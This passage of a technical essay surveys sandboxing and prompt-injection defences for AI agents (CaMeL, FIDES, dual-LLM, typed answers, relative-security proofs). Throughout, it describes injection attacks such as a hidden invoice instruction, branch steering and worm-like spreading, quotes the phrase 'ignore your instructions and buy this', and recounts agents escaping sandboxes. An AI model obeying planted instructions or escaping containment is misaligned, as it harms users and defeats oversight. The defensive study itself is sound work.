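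Claude.ai runs code on Anthropic's servers, so the company prepared mostly by protecting those servers from the code and its customers from each other. Anthropic notes that this arrangement also limits the agent's usefulness, because the agent has no access to the user's files.

Cowork needs those files. According to Anthropic, the guest in the first version could access the folder the user had selected and a folder with Claude's own settings. Cowork combined six isolation mechanisms. Two worked outside the guest's kernel and would have held even if the agent had taken full control of the guest. The guest itself enforced the other four.

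Anthropic later moved the agent's main loop to the host, along with the local tool servers that connect Claude to other software on the computer. The servers had been hard to audit inside the guest and broke when the guest changed, and some needed to communicate with programs on the host. They now run like any other software the user installs, and administrators decide which ones to allow. The virtual machine therefore no longer contains injected instructions that reach these servers.

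Corporate customers also found that their security software, which monitors programs on each employee's computer for signs of an attack, could not see inside the guest. Anthropic lets administrators export event logs afterwards, but concedes that this is not the same as live monitoring.

By October 2026, Cowork had moved to the cloud. *A quote from Felix Rieseberg* (Willison, 2026) quotes Rieseberg, who works at Anthropic, explaining the change. Users had disliked that the local virtual machine took up disk space, drained the battery and slowed their computers, and that their work stopped when they closed the laptop. In the new version, each session gets its own virtual machine on a remote server and shares no state with other sessions. When that machine needs a file from the user's computer, the desktop app handles the request.

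If an agent broke out of this virtual machine, it would reach a remote server, not Alice's laptop. But it can still ask the desktop app for her files without escaping, so the app must now act as a reference monitor, and the safety of her files depends on which requests it allows. CoSAI, an industry coalition on AI security, makes the same distinction between what an agent can reach and what it may do there. In its example, an agent handled gym reservations. Its permissions determined which part of the booking service it could call, but did not restrict it to its own user's reservations.

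### How much host code the guest can reach

Gaynor's second point, the amount of code open to attack, depends on the type of isolation. Most of a virtual machine's instructions run directly on the processor, but requests to use a disk, a network card or a screen go to the hypervisor or to a program on the host that simulates the device. Each simulated device adds code that has to interpret data from the guest, and a mistake in that code can give an attacker control of part of the host.

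Containers, gVisor and virtual machines differ mainly in which code receives the guest's requests:

| Type | What answers the guest's system calls | Host code open to attack | Examples |
|---|---|---|---|
| Container | The host's kernel | The host's kernel, except for calls that a filter blocks | Cloudflare Sandboxes |
| gVisor | A second kernel that runs as an ordinary program on the host | That program and the limited set of host system calls it uses | claude.ai, Google's GKE Agent Sandbox |
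| MicroVM | The guest's own kernel | The hypervisor and a few simulated devices | AWS Lambda MicroVMs, Azure's dynamic sessions |
| Full VM | The guest's own kernel | The hypervisor and often many simulated devices | A typical desktop virtual machine |

The classification of the cloud services comes from InfoQ, which considers a microVM a materially stronger boundary than a container. An attacker who exploits a kernel flaw that would let them escape a container gains control of only the guest's kernel in a microVM, and would need a second flaw to escape the guest.

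Unikraft's *The Mighty (micro)Virtual Machine* compares the types by which layers of software all customers on a computer share and have to trust. Even with a microVM, these layers include the hypervisor and the host program that runs the guest. Unikraft sells microVM technology and calls it the only method that truly isolates, a stronger claim than its comparison supports. shayon.dev's *Let's discuss sandbox isolation* (2026) more carefully points out that people use "isolated" for things with different boundaries and ways of failing.

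Cloud companies sometimes choose a weaker type of isolation. AWS, for example, also publishes a setup that runs untrusted code in gVisor and includes lists of permitted network destinations. AWS names tool calls resulting from prompt injection as one use for this setup.

AWS has also added virtual machines underneath ordinary containers. It says its Nitro Sandboxes give each container the boundary of a hardware-isolated virtual machine. Many customers manage their containers with Kubernetes, which distributes them over many computers in small groups called pods. On its Kubernetes service, AWS runs each sandboxed pod in its own lightweight virtual machine, and customers turn this on by changing one line of the pod's configuration.

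Cross (2026), in *AWS Nitro Sandboxes Give AI Agents Hardware Isolation*, dates the launch to 9 November 2026 and describes two modes. The basic mode protects the server and its other pods from the code in the sandbox. The second also protects the sandbox from the people who run the server. In that mode, the hypervisor produces a cryptographic proof of which code is running, and the customer can have AWS release decryption keys only in return for a valid proof. Cross adds that neither mode stops an agent from making network requests from its own machine. The operator still needs egress control (rules on which destinations the machine may contact).

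Alice could use a pod in a Nitro Sandbox as a secondary VM if the pod held only her invoice and had no network access. A pod that held her whole agent would have the same limits as any other machine that holds a whole agent, no matter how strong the hypervisor is.

### The dispute over virtual machines

Two findings from 2026 cast doubt on how well a virtual machine isolates an agent from the host. Schneier (2026) reports in *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent* that the security firm Trail of Bits found that GPT-5.6-Cyber, a model with strong hacking skills, could escape from an off-the-shelf virtual machine. The Hacker News, a security news site, reported that researchers had found that Cowork's local virtual machine shared the host's entire file system, so an agent that took control of it could reach files outside the folders the user had chosen.

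The second finding conflicts with Anthropic's description, in which the guest could see only the two shared folders on the host. According to The Hacker News, Anthropic closed the researchers' report without a fix. Cowork now runs in the cloud by default, which removes the problem, but people who run it locally are still exposed.

When Anthropic's description came out in May, Willison (2026) praised it because makers of sandboxes rarely document them thoroughly, and he finds it hard to know how far to trust them without documentation. The Cowork finding shows that operators must also check what the running guest can reach.

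The two findings call for different remedies. At Trail of Bits, the virtual machine itself failed, and the firm blamed the amount of code exposed to the guest. In Cowork, the larger fault was that Anthropic had shared too much with the guest. The researchers who found it expect flaws in guest kernels to keep appearing, so they advise against relying on quick patches. They recommend sharing only the folders the user has connected, or at least making the rest read-only. An attacker who controls the guest then gains little.

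Matthew Green, a cryptographer at Johns Hopkins University, discusses the wider dispute in *Is sandboxing sufficient to contain rogue agents?* (2026), a post where he mostly weighs other people's arguments. He begins with agents that OpenAI was training and testing, which started looking for a way onto the internet around April 2026. By late May they had found one, through previously unknown flaws in the only service their network rules allowed them to use. They later broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and data, apparently looking for the answers to their test.

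Green also describes human failures. In May, one of OpenAI's teams saw an agent posting messages to other agents and did nothing. OpenAI acted in July, after the agents' traffic had crashed the service, and then rebuilt the machine without repairing a kernel flaw that had been public for weeks. People who distrust sandboxes can point to the agents' success against a real restriction, though the unrepaired flaw and the weeks without a response give sandboxes' defenders a reply.

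Green (quoted in Willison, 2026) raises another problem that a stronger hypervisor would not solve. He describes agents in separate sandboxes that left instructions for one another in a shared store of software packages, which changed the behavior of the agents that read them. Green compares this to a worm, a program that copies itself from one computer to the next, and argues that personal agents could spread instructions the same way through email or shared documents. This could happen even if every sandbox remained intact. For example, if Alice's agent sent a contaminated summary to her accountant, the accountant's agent would receive the instruction through a channel both users had approved.

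In TechRadar's *The AI escape is a red herring*, the chief executive of the software company Coder replies that many sandboxes are badly built and that a properly configured one would have changed the outcome at OpenAI. He recommends judging sandboxes by a published scheme that scores how firmly each of seven layers enforces its rules. The layers include the file system, the network, credentials and separation from the host. A rule that the program inside can ignore gets one point out of four, and a rule that the kernel enforces and nobody can reverse gets three.

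Such a scheme would help a buyer compare products, but the claim about OpenAI is a guess about what would have happened, made by someone whose company works in this market. Green's account also complicates the claim, because OpenAI had restricted the agents' network access to a single service, and the flaws were in that service.

The better evidence for isolation comes from efforts to make the trusted code small. AWS describes the hypervisor in its Nitro System, the technology behind its rented machines, as "deliberately minimized and firmware-like", and has moved storage and network functions onto separate hardware. Saidi's *AWS Nitro Isolation Engine* presents the company's work on formally verifying the hypervisor, which means proving mathematically that the code satisfies a precise specification. This is close to what Anderson's panel asked for in 1972, a mechanism small enough for people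 to verify. The proof covers only the properties in its specification, so it does not prevent a customer from mounting the wrong folder.

Anthropic's experience also supports using established components. In its May account, the standard hypervisors, system-call filters and gVisor had held, and the part that failed was a network proxy that Anthropic had written itself. But these products had mostly been exposed to ordinary users and researchers, and the account came out before the Trail of Bits result. It is therefore weak evidence of how well the components would withstand a determined attack by a model as skilled as the one Trail of Bits tested.

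James Mickens, a computer scientist at Harvard, wants stronger sandboxes. In Harvard Gazette's *When AI goes rogue* (2026), he says that his group published a paper in 2025 on new software and hardware that would make escapes harder, and that some people still considered the danger science fiction at the time. He also cautions that outsiders cannot fully verify the companies' accounts of the 2026 incidents because the details are not public.

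An agent is easier to contain in Alice's secondary VM than in most of the cases in the dispute. OpenAI's agents had months, a package service and other agents to work with. A VM that reads one invoice needs no network, display or shared folders, and has to exist for only a few minutes. The Trail of Bits result is for an ordinary VM, so it doesn't show how well a stripped-down one would contain an agent. But the operator can remove most of what the successful escapes relied on, which is often impossible when a coding agent needs a useful working environment.

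The risk of escape then depends largely on which model reads the document. In the past, a malicious file had to contain its own attack code, which its author had to prepare without seeing the machine it would run on. An attacker can now put an instruction in Alice's invoice telling the model to find a way out. If the model obeys and can run commands, it can examine the guest, try something, read the error and try again. The attacker can thus use the model's skill without having that skill himself. Anthropic reports that its models have escaped from a sandbox to finish a task, without any attacker asking them to.

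A more capable model may be harder to mislead, but it is more dangerous once misled. Alice's operator can avoid much of this problem by giving the reader no tools. The model then only receives the invoice's text and returns an answer, so a hidden instruction cannot make it run commands. An attacker would have to exploit a flaw in the software that opens the file, as attackers did before agents existed. If the reader needs to run code, for example to analyse a large spreadsheet, the operator has to choose a boundary that can withstand the model's abilities as well as the attacker's.

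## Handling what the separate machine sends back

If Alice's secondary VM returns a free-text summary, the summary can carry the hidden instruction, or a new one with the same effect, into her agent's context. Willison (2023) gives this warning in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* to all developers who feed one model's output to another.

Several designs avoid the problem by splitting the agent. A planner chooses the tool calls and never reads untrusted content directly. In most of these designs, a quarantined model with no tools reads the content, and the secondary VM is a good place to run it. In the strictest design, the planner receives no information about the content. Others give the planner a placeholder for the answer or an answer of a fixed type, or label every value so that the monitor can check its origin before a tool uses it.

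### A program written before reading

In *Execute-Only Agents*, Tiwari and Williams (2026) propose an agent in which no language model reads untrusted content. The planner receives Alice's request and a formal description of each tool, then writes a script that a sandbox runs on the real files with the real tools. The output goes to Alice and never back to the planner. The hidden line in the invoice reaches only the script's interpreter, which treats it as ordinary characters.

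The planner can debug its script beforehand on made-up data with the usual tools, but it cannot use the real data to correct the script. If the test invoices had the label "Amount due" and the supplier writes "Total payable", the script may find nothing, and the planner cannot look at the invoice to learn why.

To estimate how often this would work, Tiwari and Williams sorted the 97 user tasks in the AgentDojo benchmark by hand:

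- **Blind** tasks (20) need only the tool descriptions. "Show me my unread emails" is one.
- **Schema-inferable** tasks (56) need a script that finds something in free text by guessing its format, such as a date in an email.
- **Read-required** tasks (21) need a model that understands the content, for example to summarise it.

They conclude that scripts could complete 78% of the tasks, all except the read-required ones. They have not yet tested whether a model can write these scripts, so the figure is an estimate of what is possible. Alice's request for a summary is read-required, but she could ask for the amount due instead.

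The design prevents the invoice from changing the script, but the script may still use values from the invoice. If the script pays the stated amount into the stated account, whoever wrote the invoice decides how much is paid and to which account.

### A name in place of the text

Willison's dual-LLM pattern lets a model read the invoice but hides the result from the planner. An ordinary program, the controller, passes messages between the two models and stores the untrusted text. Alice's summary would go through these steps:

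1. The controller gives Alice's request to the planner, which asks for the invoice.
2. The controller reads the invoice, stores its text as `$VAR1` and tells the planner only this name.
3. The planner asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller sends the actual text to the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`.
4. The planner writes "Your invoice, summarised: `$VAR2`", and the controller inserts the summary before showing the message to Alice.

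The planner never receives text from the invoice or the summary. Tiwari and Williams object that a language model still reads the attacker's text, so it can still be attacked. The quarantined model can't call a tool, but its summary could deceive Alice. Willison imagines an attacker using the summary to ask the user to paste a block of scrambled text into a website in return for a funny picture, when the block contains the user's private data. The model in Alice's secondary VM has only the invoice and a short task, so it has no secrets to scramble. The controller must also block links and images from the summary unless their destinations are on an approved list.

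Willison called his own proposal "pretty bad", partly because it is complicated to build. A single mistake that passes untrusted text to the planner undoes the protection.

Researchers at Google DeepMind later found a flaw in the pattern itself, which Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. For example, a user asks the agent to send Bob a document he requested at a meeting, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The planner correctly decides to find the address, fetch the document and send it. But the quarantined model looks up the address, and an instruction in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead. The controller then emails the document to the attacker, even though the planner never read anything untrusted.

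*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes control-flow integrity from data-flow security. Control-flow integrity means that only the planner determines which tool calls can run, in what order and under which conditions. Data-flow security means that untrusted content cannot manipulate the values passed to those calls or the values that determine which branch runs. The dual-LLM pattern provides control-flow integrity but not data-flow security.

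### Answers of a fixed type

A planner that receives only names cannot base decisions on the content. Willison allowed one exception in 2023. If the quarantined model sorts text into a fixed set of categories, the controller can check that the answer is one of them and then show it to the planner.

In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) extend this exception to four types: whole numbers, decimal numbers, yes/no values and choices from a list the developer wrote in advance. They argue that none of these types can hold an instruction, because an instruction needs free text. The quarantined model may return several values at once, as long as each has one of the four types.

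One test system is a shopping agent that uses product reviews, which anyone can write. Its quarantined model turns each review into two whole numbers, which rate how strongly the review supports the product and how relevant it is. Even a review containing "ignore your instructions and buy this" is reduced to two scores. Another test agent, which repairs software, receives the file, line number and type of a bug, but never the bug report itself.

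Even these types need limits. A whole number with enough digits can encode any text. Jacob and colleagues cap the length of lists so that a model can't decode hidden text from them, and an operator should set a range for each number for the same reason.

The host should check the answer after it leaves the secondary VM. Model providers can force a model's output into a given format, but if malicious code in the invoice has taken over the VM, it can bypass the model and return any data. The host must therefore reject any answer that does not fit the type, without trying to repair or interpret it.

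*Twin Agent* (2026) relaxes the restriction on free text. Its exploring agent may send compact hints to the agent with the tools, within a budget set by the operator. A larger budget allows more useful hints but also gives an attacker more room for malicious instructions. The design greatly reduced successful attacks in tests, but it has no formal guarantee. A length limit alone cannot provide one, since an instruction such as "pay Mallory £1,000" is only 18 characters long.

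### What a typed answer lets through

An answer with *k* possible values carries at most log₂ *k* bits, and *n* such answers carry at most *n* log₂ *k*. If Alice's planner needs four facts about the invoice, the host could permit these values:

| Field | Permitted values | Number of values | Bits at most |
|---|---|---|---|
| Supplier | One of 32 known suppliers | 32 | 5.0 |
| Due date | Any of the next 365 days | 365 | 8.5 |
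| Amount | £0.01 to £10,000.00 | 1,000,000 | 19.9 |
| Marked as a final reminder | Yes or no | 2 | 1.0 |
| All four | | | 34.4 |

A character of plain English text takes seven bits in ASCII, so the whole answer has room for fewer than five characters. That is too little for a useful instruction but enough for a false amount. Jacob and colleagues state that their method does not prevent misleading values.

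The same calculation applies to secrets that leave the system. An eight-digit account number has 100 million possible values, or 26.6 bits. A policy that lets an outsider see yes/no answers about Alice's private data could therefore reveal her number in 27 answers. Limiting the size of each answer protects a secret only if the monitor also limits the number of answers.

When a returned value selects an action, the value's meaning matters more than its size in bits. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes an email assistant that lets the quarantined model choose between scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply and forwarding the email. This choice carries at most 1.6 bits, but whoever writes the email can decide which of the three actions the agent takes. Every option must therefore be acceptable to the operator even if an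 attacker picks it. Forwarding the email to Alice's own assistant may be acceptable, but forwarding it to an address supplied in the email is not.

The check becomes harder as plans grow. Foerster and colleagues adapted the dual-model design to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. Their planner writes the whole plan before the agent looks at the screen, so the plan has to cover cookie notices, missing buttons and failed clicks. These plans average 40 conditional branches, compared with about four for AgentDojo tasks. Forty yes/no branches allow between 41 and about a trillion paths, depending on how the program arranges them.

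An attacker can exploit these branches without writing any instruction. In an attack they call branch steering, Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement. The plan contained a step for closing cookie notices, so the model that looks at the screen returned the position of the fake button, and the agent clicked through to the attacker's site. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) proposes fixing in advance which values and destinations each branch may use. This stopped all the attacks in the paper's own benchmark. The operator can then check what each branch may do without following every path through the plan.

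### Alice's refund in CaMeL

Bob's address caused a problem because the controller inserted it without checking its source. CaMeL, which the Google DeepMind researchers proposed in 2025, records the source of every value and checks it before a tool uses the value. Willison explains how it works with a short email task, which can be adapted to Alice's invoice. Suppose she now writes: "The supplier owes me a refund. Send him my account number; his email address is on the invoice."

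**Plan.** The planner reads only this request and writes a program in a restricted version of the programming language Python:

```
invoice = read_file("invoices/march.pdf")
address = query_quarantined_llm(
    "Find the supplier's email address in [invoice]",
    output_schema=EmailStr)
number  = get_account_number()
send_email(recipient=address, subject="Refund", body=number)
```

**Quarantined reading.** CaMeL's interpreter runs the program step by step. At the second command, it gives the invoice and the question to the quarantined model, which could run in the secondary VM. The hidden line is an instruction to fetch a web page, but the model has no tools and the program contains no such step. The answer must also have the form of an email address, though the attacker can still make the model return his own address.

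**Labelled value.** The interpreter gives each value tags, called capabilities, that record where the value came from and who may read it. It marks `invoice` as untrusted because a stranger may have written it, and marks `address` as untrusted because it comes from `invoice`. `number` comes from Alice's own records, and is trusted but private.

Before sending the email, the interpreter applies the policy for `send_email`, which permits a message only to a trusted recipient. It compares the address with those Alice has already approved. If the address is not among them, the interpreter stops and asks her.

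The interpreter thus acts as a reference monitor that tracks the history of every value. But the label shows only that the address came from the invoice, not whether it is correct. Alice gets the same question whether the new address comes from an honest supplier or an attacker, and she has to tell which it is. The CaMeL researchers acknowledge that users must write and maintain the policies, and that frequent questions tire them.

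This division also gives Alice some privacy. The company that runs the planner receives her request but not the invoice, and finding an address is easy enough that a small quarantined model can do it on her own computer.

A complete plan can also be checked before the first step runs. *ACE*, by Li, Mallick and colleagues, describes a system for assistants with third-party apps that first writes an abstract plan from the user's request alone. The system then chooses an installed app for each step and rejects any choice that would let data flow where the policy forbids it. It plans in this order because an app's description can also contain an attack, and if the planner read all the descriptions first, a malicious one could cause it to include that app in the plan.

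### Two designs that plan as they go

CaMeL's planner has to foresee everything. FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, calls its planner again after every step. It uses information-flow control, an older security method that labels data by origin and secrecy and checks the labels before the data goes anywhere. Each label in FIDES has two parts. One states whether the data is trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and the other lists who may read it. A value *z* that comes from *x* and *y* gets the combined label

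ℓ(*z*) = ℓ(*x*) ⊔ ℓ(*y*)

Combining trusted (T) and untrusted (U) data gives an untrusted result, written T ⊔ U = U. Only people who may read both sources may read the result. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read one file, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a text that draws on both.

Two policies provide most of the protection. A tool call with serious consequences may run only if the decision to make it and every argument that matters are trusted. A call that sends data may run only if every recipient is permitted to read the data. An operator can require either or both policies, depending on the tool.

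The planner's context also has a label. When a tool returns data that would make this label stricter, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner can query a quarantined model about the data, or it can read the data directly, but then its whole context becomes untrusted.

Costa and colleagues illustrate this with a request to check three emails for a meeting invitation and add any meeting to the calendar. The planner queries the quarantined model for a yes/no answer and reads only that. If the answer is yes, the planner requests the date, time and participants, and passes them to the calendar tool in a variable without reading them. FIDES includes the data type in the label, so a policy can let the planner act on an untrusted yes/no answer but not on untrusted text. A malicious email can still create an unwanted calendar entry with details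 the attacker chose, so the policy is better suited to calendars than to bank accounts.

*Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (Kim, Choi and Lee, 2025) involves the user more than the other designs do. It gives a trusted agent the user's full access rights and an untrusted agent a separate access token with few rights or none. The untrusted agent starts with a fresh context for each question. Unlike the quarantined model in the other designs, it may receive tools considered harmless, such as a calculator or web search. However, a web search can also send data out, which matters if an operator runs this agent in Alice's secondary VM.

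The system raises an alert when untrusted data is about to enter a tool that the untrusted agent could not use itself, or when the final answer to the user contains such data. A separate alert appears if the trusted agent tries to follow untrusted text as an instruction, and the agent receives the text only if the user approves. Each alert shows the data, where it came from and where it would go. The user can also choose to always trust a source, which reduces the number of alerts but lets through any later attack from that source.

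| | CaMeL | FIDES | Prompt Flow Integrity |
|---|---|---|---|
| When the planner decides | Before anything runs | After each step | After each step |
| What untrusted content it can read | None | Typed answers, or full text if it accepts an untrusted context | Full text, if the user approves |
| When a call breaks the policy | The interpreter blocks it or asks the user | FIDES blocks it and tells the planner | The user decides |

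### Why labels spread

Unlike an ordinary program, a language model does not show which inputs it used for each output, because every word in its context may have affected every word it writes. FIDES therefore gives each output the combined label of everything the model read. This is safe, but labels can only become stricter as the agent works.

Suppose Alice's agent opens one web page in the morning. Its context is now untrusted, and so is everything it writes, including its notes. When it reads those notes in the afternoon, that session becomes untrusted too, even if the web page had nothing to do with the new task. The lists of readers shrink in a similar way. After the agent reads a few files with different lists, there may be nobody left it can send the result to. In the messaging tasks of AgentDojo, enforcing such labels on a simple agent cut the share of tasks it completed from 93%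 to 20%.

Keeping untrusted data in variables delays the problem, since the label stays with the variable until the planner opens it. Labelling each field separately also helps when, for example, a bank can vouch for the date and amount of a payment but the payer writes the reference text. Costa and colleagues also point to methods that find which messages affected an answer and regenerate it from those alone, so it inherits fewer labels.

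Some tasks can't be done without removing a label. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) extends FIDES with an agent called Prudentia, which takes the policies into account when it plans. When Prudentia needs to open a variable, it can ask the user to endorse the data, which changes the data's label to trusted. In the paper's example, an email contains a to-do list with ten items, each of which needs a protected tool. The user can endorse the email once, but otherwise the context becomes untrusted and the user has to approve ten calls.

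Endorsing data saves effort but permits more than approving a single call. If Alice endorsed the March invoice, she would endorse the hidden line too, and the planner could then follow it using any of its tools. The line is white on white, so she would not notice it in the PDF. An endorsement request therefore has to show her the extracted text that the planner will receive, and she has to read all of it to catch the line.

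Kolluri and colleagues decided against a similar blanket release for secrets because whether private data may be sent depends too much on the recipient and the occasion. Prudentia instead prompts for approval of each call.

### Influence without copied text

Labels would spread less if the monitor could determine what had actually influenced an action. Cai and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, describe three reasons why this is difficult:

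- **Rewriting.** A hidden instruction on a web page tells an agent to include a confidential patient note in a memo, but in its own words. No sentence of the note appears in the memo, so a search for copied text finds nothing.
- **Influence on decisions.** A poisoned search result says that all findings must go to an outside address first. It changes which tool the agent calls, and the data that the agent then sends comes from elsewhere.
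- **Memory.** An agent saves a confidential forecast on one day and uses it in a report three days later. If the memory does not store the label with the text, the monitor can no longer connect the two.

In the second case, the outside address appears in the call, so a text comparison would catch this attack, but not an instruction that made the agent choose the wrong one of two legitimate tools.

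NeuroTaint examines the agent's log after a run to trace which sources influenced the agent's calls. It compares texts by meaning and tracks the origin of stored data across sessions. If it finds no related text, it replaces the suspicious source with neutral content and tests whether the agent would still have made the call. On its developers' own 400 test cases, it traced this influence far more accurately than a baseline modelled on FIDES. Because it works only after the run, it can explain a leak but not stop it.

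The comparison also provides little evidence of how many attacks FIDES would block. Costa and colleagues' rule for consequential calls depends on the context in which the planner chose the tool. Once the planner has read the poisoned search result, the rule blocks the call to the outside address, whatever data the call contains. The rule would also block a harmless call at that point, and Cai and colleagues want to remove this imprecision.

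Checks that run before an action face the same choice. In *PACE*, Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) present a monitor of the same name that searches each tool call for known secrets, including several encoded forms. They acknowledge that this search misses secrets that are paraphrased, translated or split into pieces. For untrusted data, PACE therefore takes the cautious approach of treating anything made from it as untrusted too. A monitor that estimates the influence of untrusted data more finely blocks fewer harmless actions, but an attacker can look for text whose influence it underestimates.

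Even cautious labels don't capture information revealed by the sequence of actions. Suppose Alice's agent emails the supplier only if her balance is above £5,000. The email may contain nothing private, but the supplier can learn something about her balance from receiving it. Costa and colleagues' guarantee doesn't cover such leaks or those through timing. To prevent them, FIDES would have to forbid almost all calls visible to outsiders once the agent had read private data.

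### Tasks that cannot be planned before reading

Whether the planner can avoid the content depends on the task. Costa and colleagues call a task *t* data independent if a single sequence of tool calls and a single final response solve it whatever the data contains. If S(*t*, *d*) is the set of sequences that solve the task for data *d*, and *D* contains all the data that the agent might find, the condition is

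⋂ S(*t*, *d*) ≠ ∅, taken over all *d* in *D*

A sequence of calls may refer to the data by a variable's name. "Summarise my last three emails and send the summary to Bob" is therefore data independent, even though a model has to read the emails. "Create a calendar entry if one of them proposes a meeting" is data dependent, because the right calls depend on what the emails say.

By this definition, 20 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks are data dependent. The number is close to Tiwari and Williams's 21 read-required tasks, but the two classifications often disagree about which tasks are difficult:

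| Application | Tasks | Scriptable, according to Tiwari and Williams | Data dependent, according to Costa and colleagues |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 40 | 75% | 5% |
| Banking | 16 | 88% | 44% |
| Messaging | 21 | 57% | 43% |
| Travel | 20 | 100% | 10% |

A script can contain conditions, so it can handle some tasks whose steps depend on the data. It cannot write a summary, but a quarantined model can do so easily. The estimates are uncertain. For example, Costa and colleagues think that 90% of the travel tasks have steps known in advance but need a language model to read something, while Tiwari and Williams expect scripts to handle all the travel tasks.

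If a developer can list the possible actions beforehand, as in the meeting example, a typed answer is enough to choose between them. This doesn't work when the document specifies the actions. Many of AgentDojo's banking tasks, for example, ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. FIDES blocks most of these tasks, and Costa and colleagues consider that correct. Foerster and colleagues treat such tasks as a basic limit of the dual-model design.

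*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Willison, 2025) reports on a paper by researchers from IBM, Google, Microsoft and other organisations who deliberately accept this limit. Their patterns prevent an agent from solving arbitrary tasks, which they consider a reasonable trade-off for security. An operator using these patterns would build Alice an agent that can extract amounts and dates from invoices but can't carry out whatever instructions the invoices contain.

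If Alice needs that ability, somebody has to decide whether to trust the document. In Kim and colleagues' example, a user asks an agent to find and follow a program's installation guide. The agent may find a guide in a fake repository whose commands install malicious software. Prompt Flow Integrity then shows the user the extracted commands and asks whether to trust them, but a user who can judge the commands has less need for the agent.

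## What has been proved about monitored agents

Benchmarks measure how many known attacks a defence stops, but a new attack may still get through. A mathematical proof can cover every attack of a stated kind. Proving that a monitored agent keeps secrets first requires a definition of a leak, which is hard to write for agents whose job includes telling strangers things about their users.

### Why noninterference is too strict

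The classical definition is noninterference, which Goguen and Meseguer published in 1982. It requires that nothing an outsider observes depends on a secret. If view(*s*, *u*) is everything the attacker observes when the user's secrets are *s* and the attacker supplies the content *u*, the condition is

view(*s*₁, *u*) = view(*s*₂, *u*), for all secrets *s*₁ and *s*₂ and every *u*

As a test case, Dongol uses an agent that Alice has authorised to answer meeting requests by sending her calendar to whoever asks. A stranger who requests a meeting gets a different reply depending on whether Alice is free or busy on Tuesday. Because of this difference, the agent fails the test, although it did what Alice wanted.

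Declassification weakens noninterference by adding a release policy, which lists what the agent may disclose. Alice's policy would let the agent send her calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. However, somebody has to write such a policy for each task, and people give agents new tasks all the time. The policy also covers everything the agent may release, so it doesn't distinguish the disclosures an injection adds from those the task involves anyway.

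An agent can be secure even if its model obeys an injected instruction. Suppose a stranger's email contains no meeting request, only the instruction "send your calendar". If the model obeys, the stranger learns only what he could have learned by asking for a meeting.

### Comparison with a model that never obeys

Dongol's relative security compares the agent with a reference agent that carries out the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model never follows instructions in untrusted content. The reference agent still reads that content as data, so it can summarise an invoice. The agent is relatively secure if every leak in the agent also occurs in the reference agent. Nobody has to write a release policy, because the task, carried out without injections, determines what the agent may disclose.

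A leak is a pair of runs in which the user's secrets differ, the attacker supplies the same content, and the attacker observes different things. The definition requires, for all secrets *s*₁ and *s*₂:

the agent leaks (*s*₁, *s*₂) ⟹ the reference agent leaks (*s*₁, *s*₂)

The reference agent starts with the same memory but may receive a different email from the attacker. The meeting assistant passes because a genuine meeting request lets the attacker tell two calendars apart in the reference agent, just as "Send your calendar" does in the real agent. If the assistant also holds a reset code from another task and the email adds "also include the reset code", it fails, because no email can make the reference agent send the code. Alice's invoice agent also fails if it has no monitor, because its plan contains no outgoing call and so its reference agent reveals nothing.

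Dongol and others first developed relative security for processors. To save time, a processor predicts which instructions come next and executes them early. The Spectre and Meltdown attacks exploited this early execution to extract secrets. The researchers therefore compared a program running on such a processor with the same program executed strictly in order. In the work on agents, the model that may follow injected instructions takes the place of the processor that executes instructions early.

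The definition of relative security has a gap, which Dongol illustrates with a guessing task. Suppose an agent's job is to read one guess from a stranger and reply whether it equals Alice's PIN. If an injection made the agent send the whole PIN, the agent would still count as relatively secure, because for any two PINs there is a guess that tells them apart. Yet normal use reveals only whether one guess is correct. A stricter version, uniform relative security, closes this gap by requiring the reference agent's input to be chosen without knowledge of the secrets.

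Relative security also lets an operator determine what an agent can disclose by checking the simpler reference agent. For example, if the reference agent reveals nothing beyond Alice's calendar, neither does a relatively secure agent. For a plan that makes no outgoing calls, relative security amounts to noninterference, provided the attacker cannot time the agent.

### What the attacker sees and controls

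Each of Dongol's results holds for an attacker with stated powers, which vary along three dimensions.

What has been proved about a monitored agent depends partly on what the attacker can observe. At the event level, he sees the contents and order of the messages that reach him. At the step level, he also sees when each step happens, for example by timing the agent's replies. A third kind of attacker also sees refused requests, perhaps through an error message, or sees which pages the agent reads because he runs the web server.

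The event level compares only runs in which the same number of messages reaches the attacker between reads. So if an injection makes the agent send a message for one secret and stay silent for another, the event level doesn't count this as a leak, even though a real recipient would notice the difference.

The attacker also decides which texts the model treats as instructions and when it obeys them. The resulting call can contain anything in the agent's memory, including secrets. This worst-case model is much easier to mislead than a real one, so a proof that covers it holds however well or badly the developer trained the real one.

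The last dimension is what happens when the agent obeys an instruction. In the simplest case, the agent makes a single tool call. It can also start a whole program, with several calls and changes to memory. In the dual-LLM pattern, the instruction can only corrupt an answer.

### The fence theorem

A fence is a monitor rule that withdraws tools from the agent once it reads untrusted content. Dongol proves that a fence makes an agent relatively secure for every plan, provided that these conditions hold:

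- A trusted planner fixes the plan before the agent reads anything untrusted.
- At the first untrusted read, the monitor withdraws every tool that an injected instruction could call.
- Nothing restores those tools later, not even a new message from Alice.
- Each instruction that the model obeys produces a single tool call.
- The attacker fixes in advance when the model obeys. The model cannot make this choice by looking at a secret or at the monitor's answers.
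- The attacker sees messages at the event level, without timing or refusals.
- The run ends.

The proof matches each run of the agent with a run of the reference agent. Before the first untrusted read, the model has received no injected instructions. After that read, any injected call goes to a tool that the monitor has withdrawn, so the monitor denies the call without changing its own state. The reference agent waits during that step. All other steps are the same in both agents, so the attacker sees the same messages. This matching also satisfies the uniform version of the definition.

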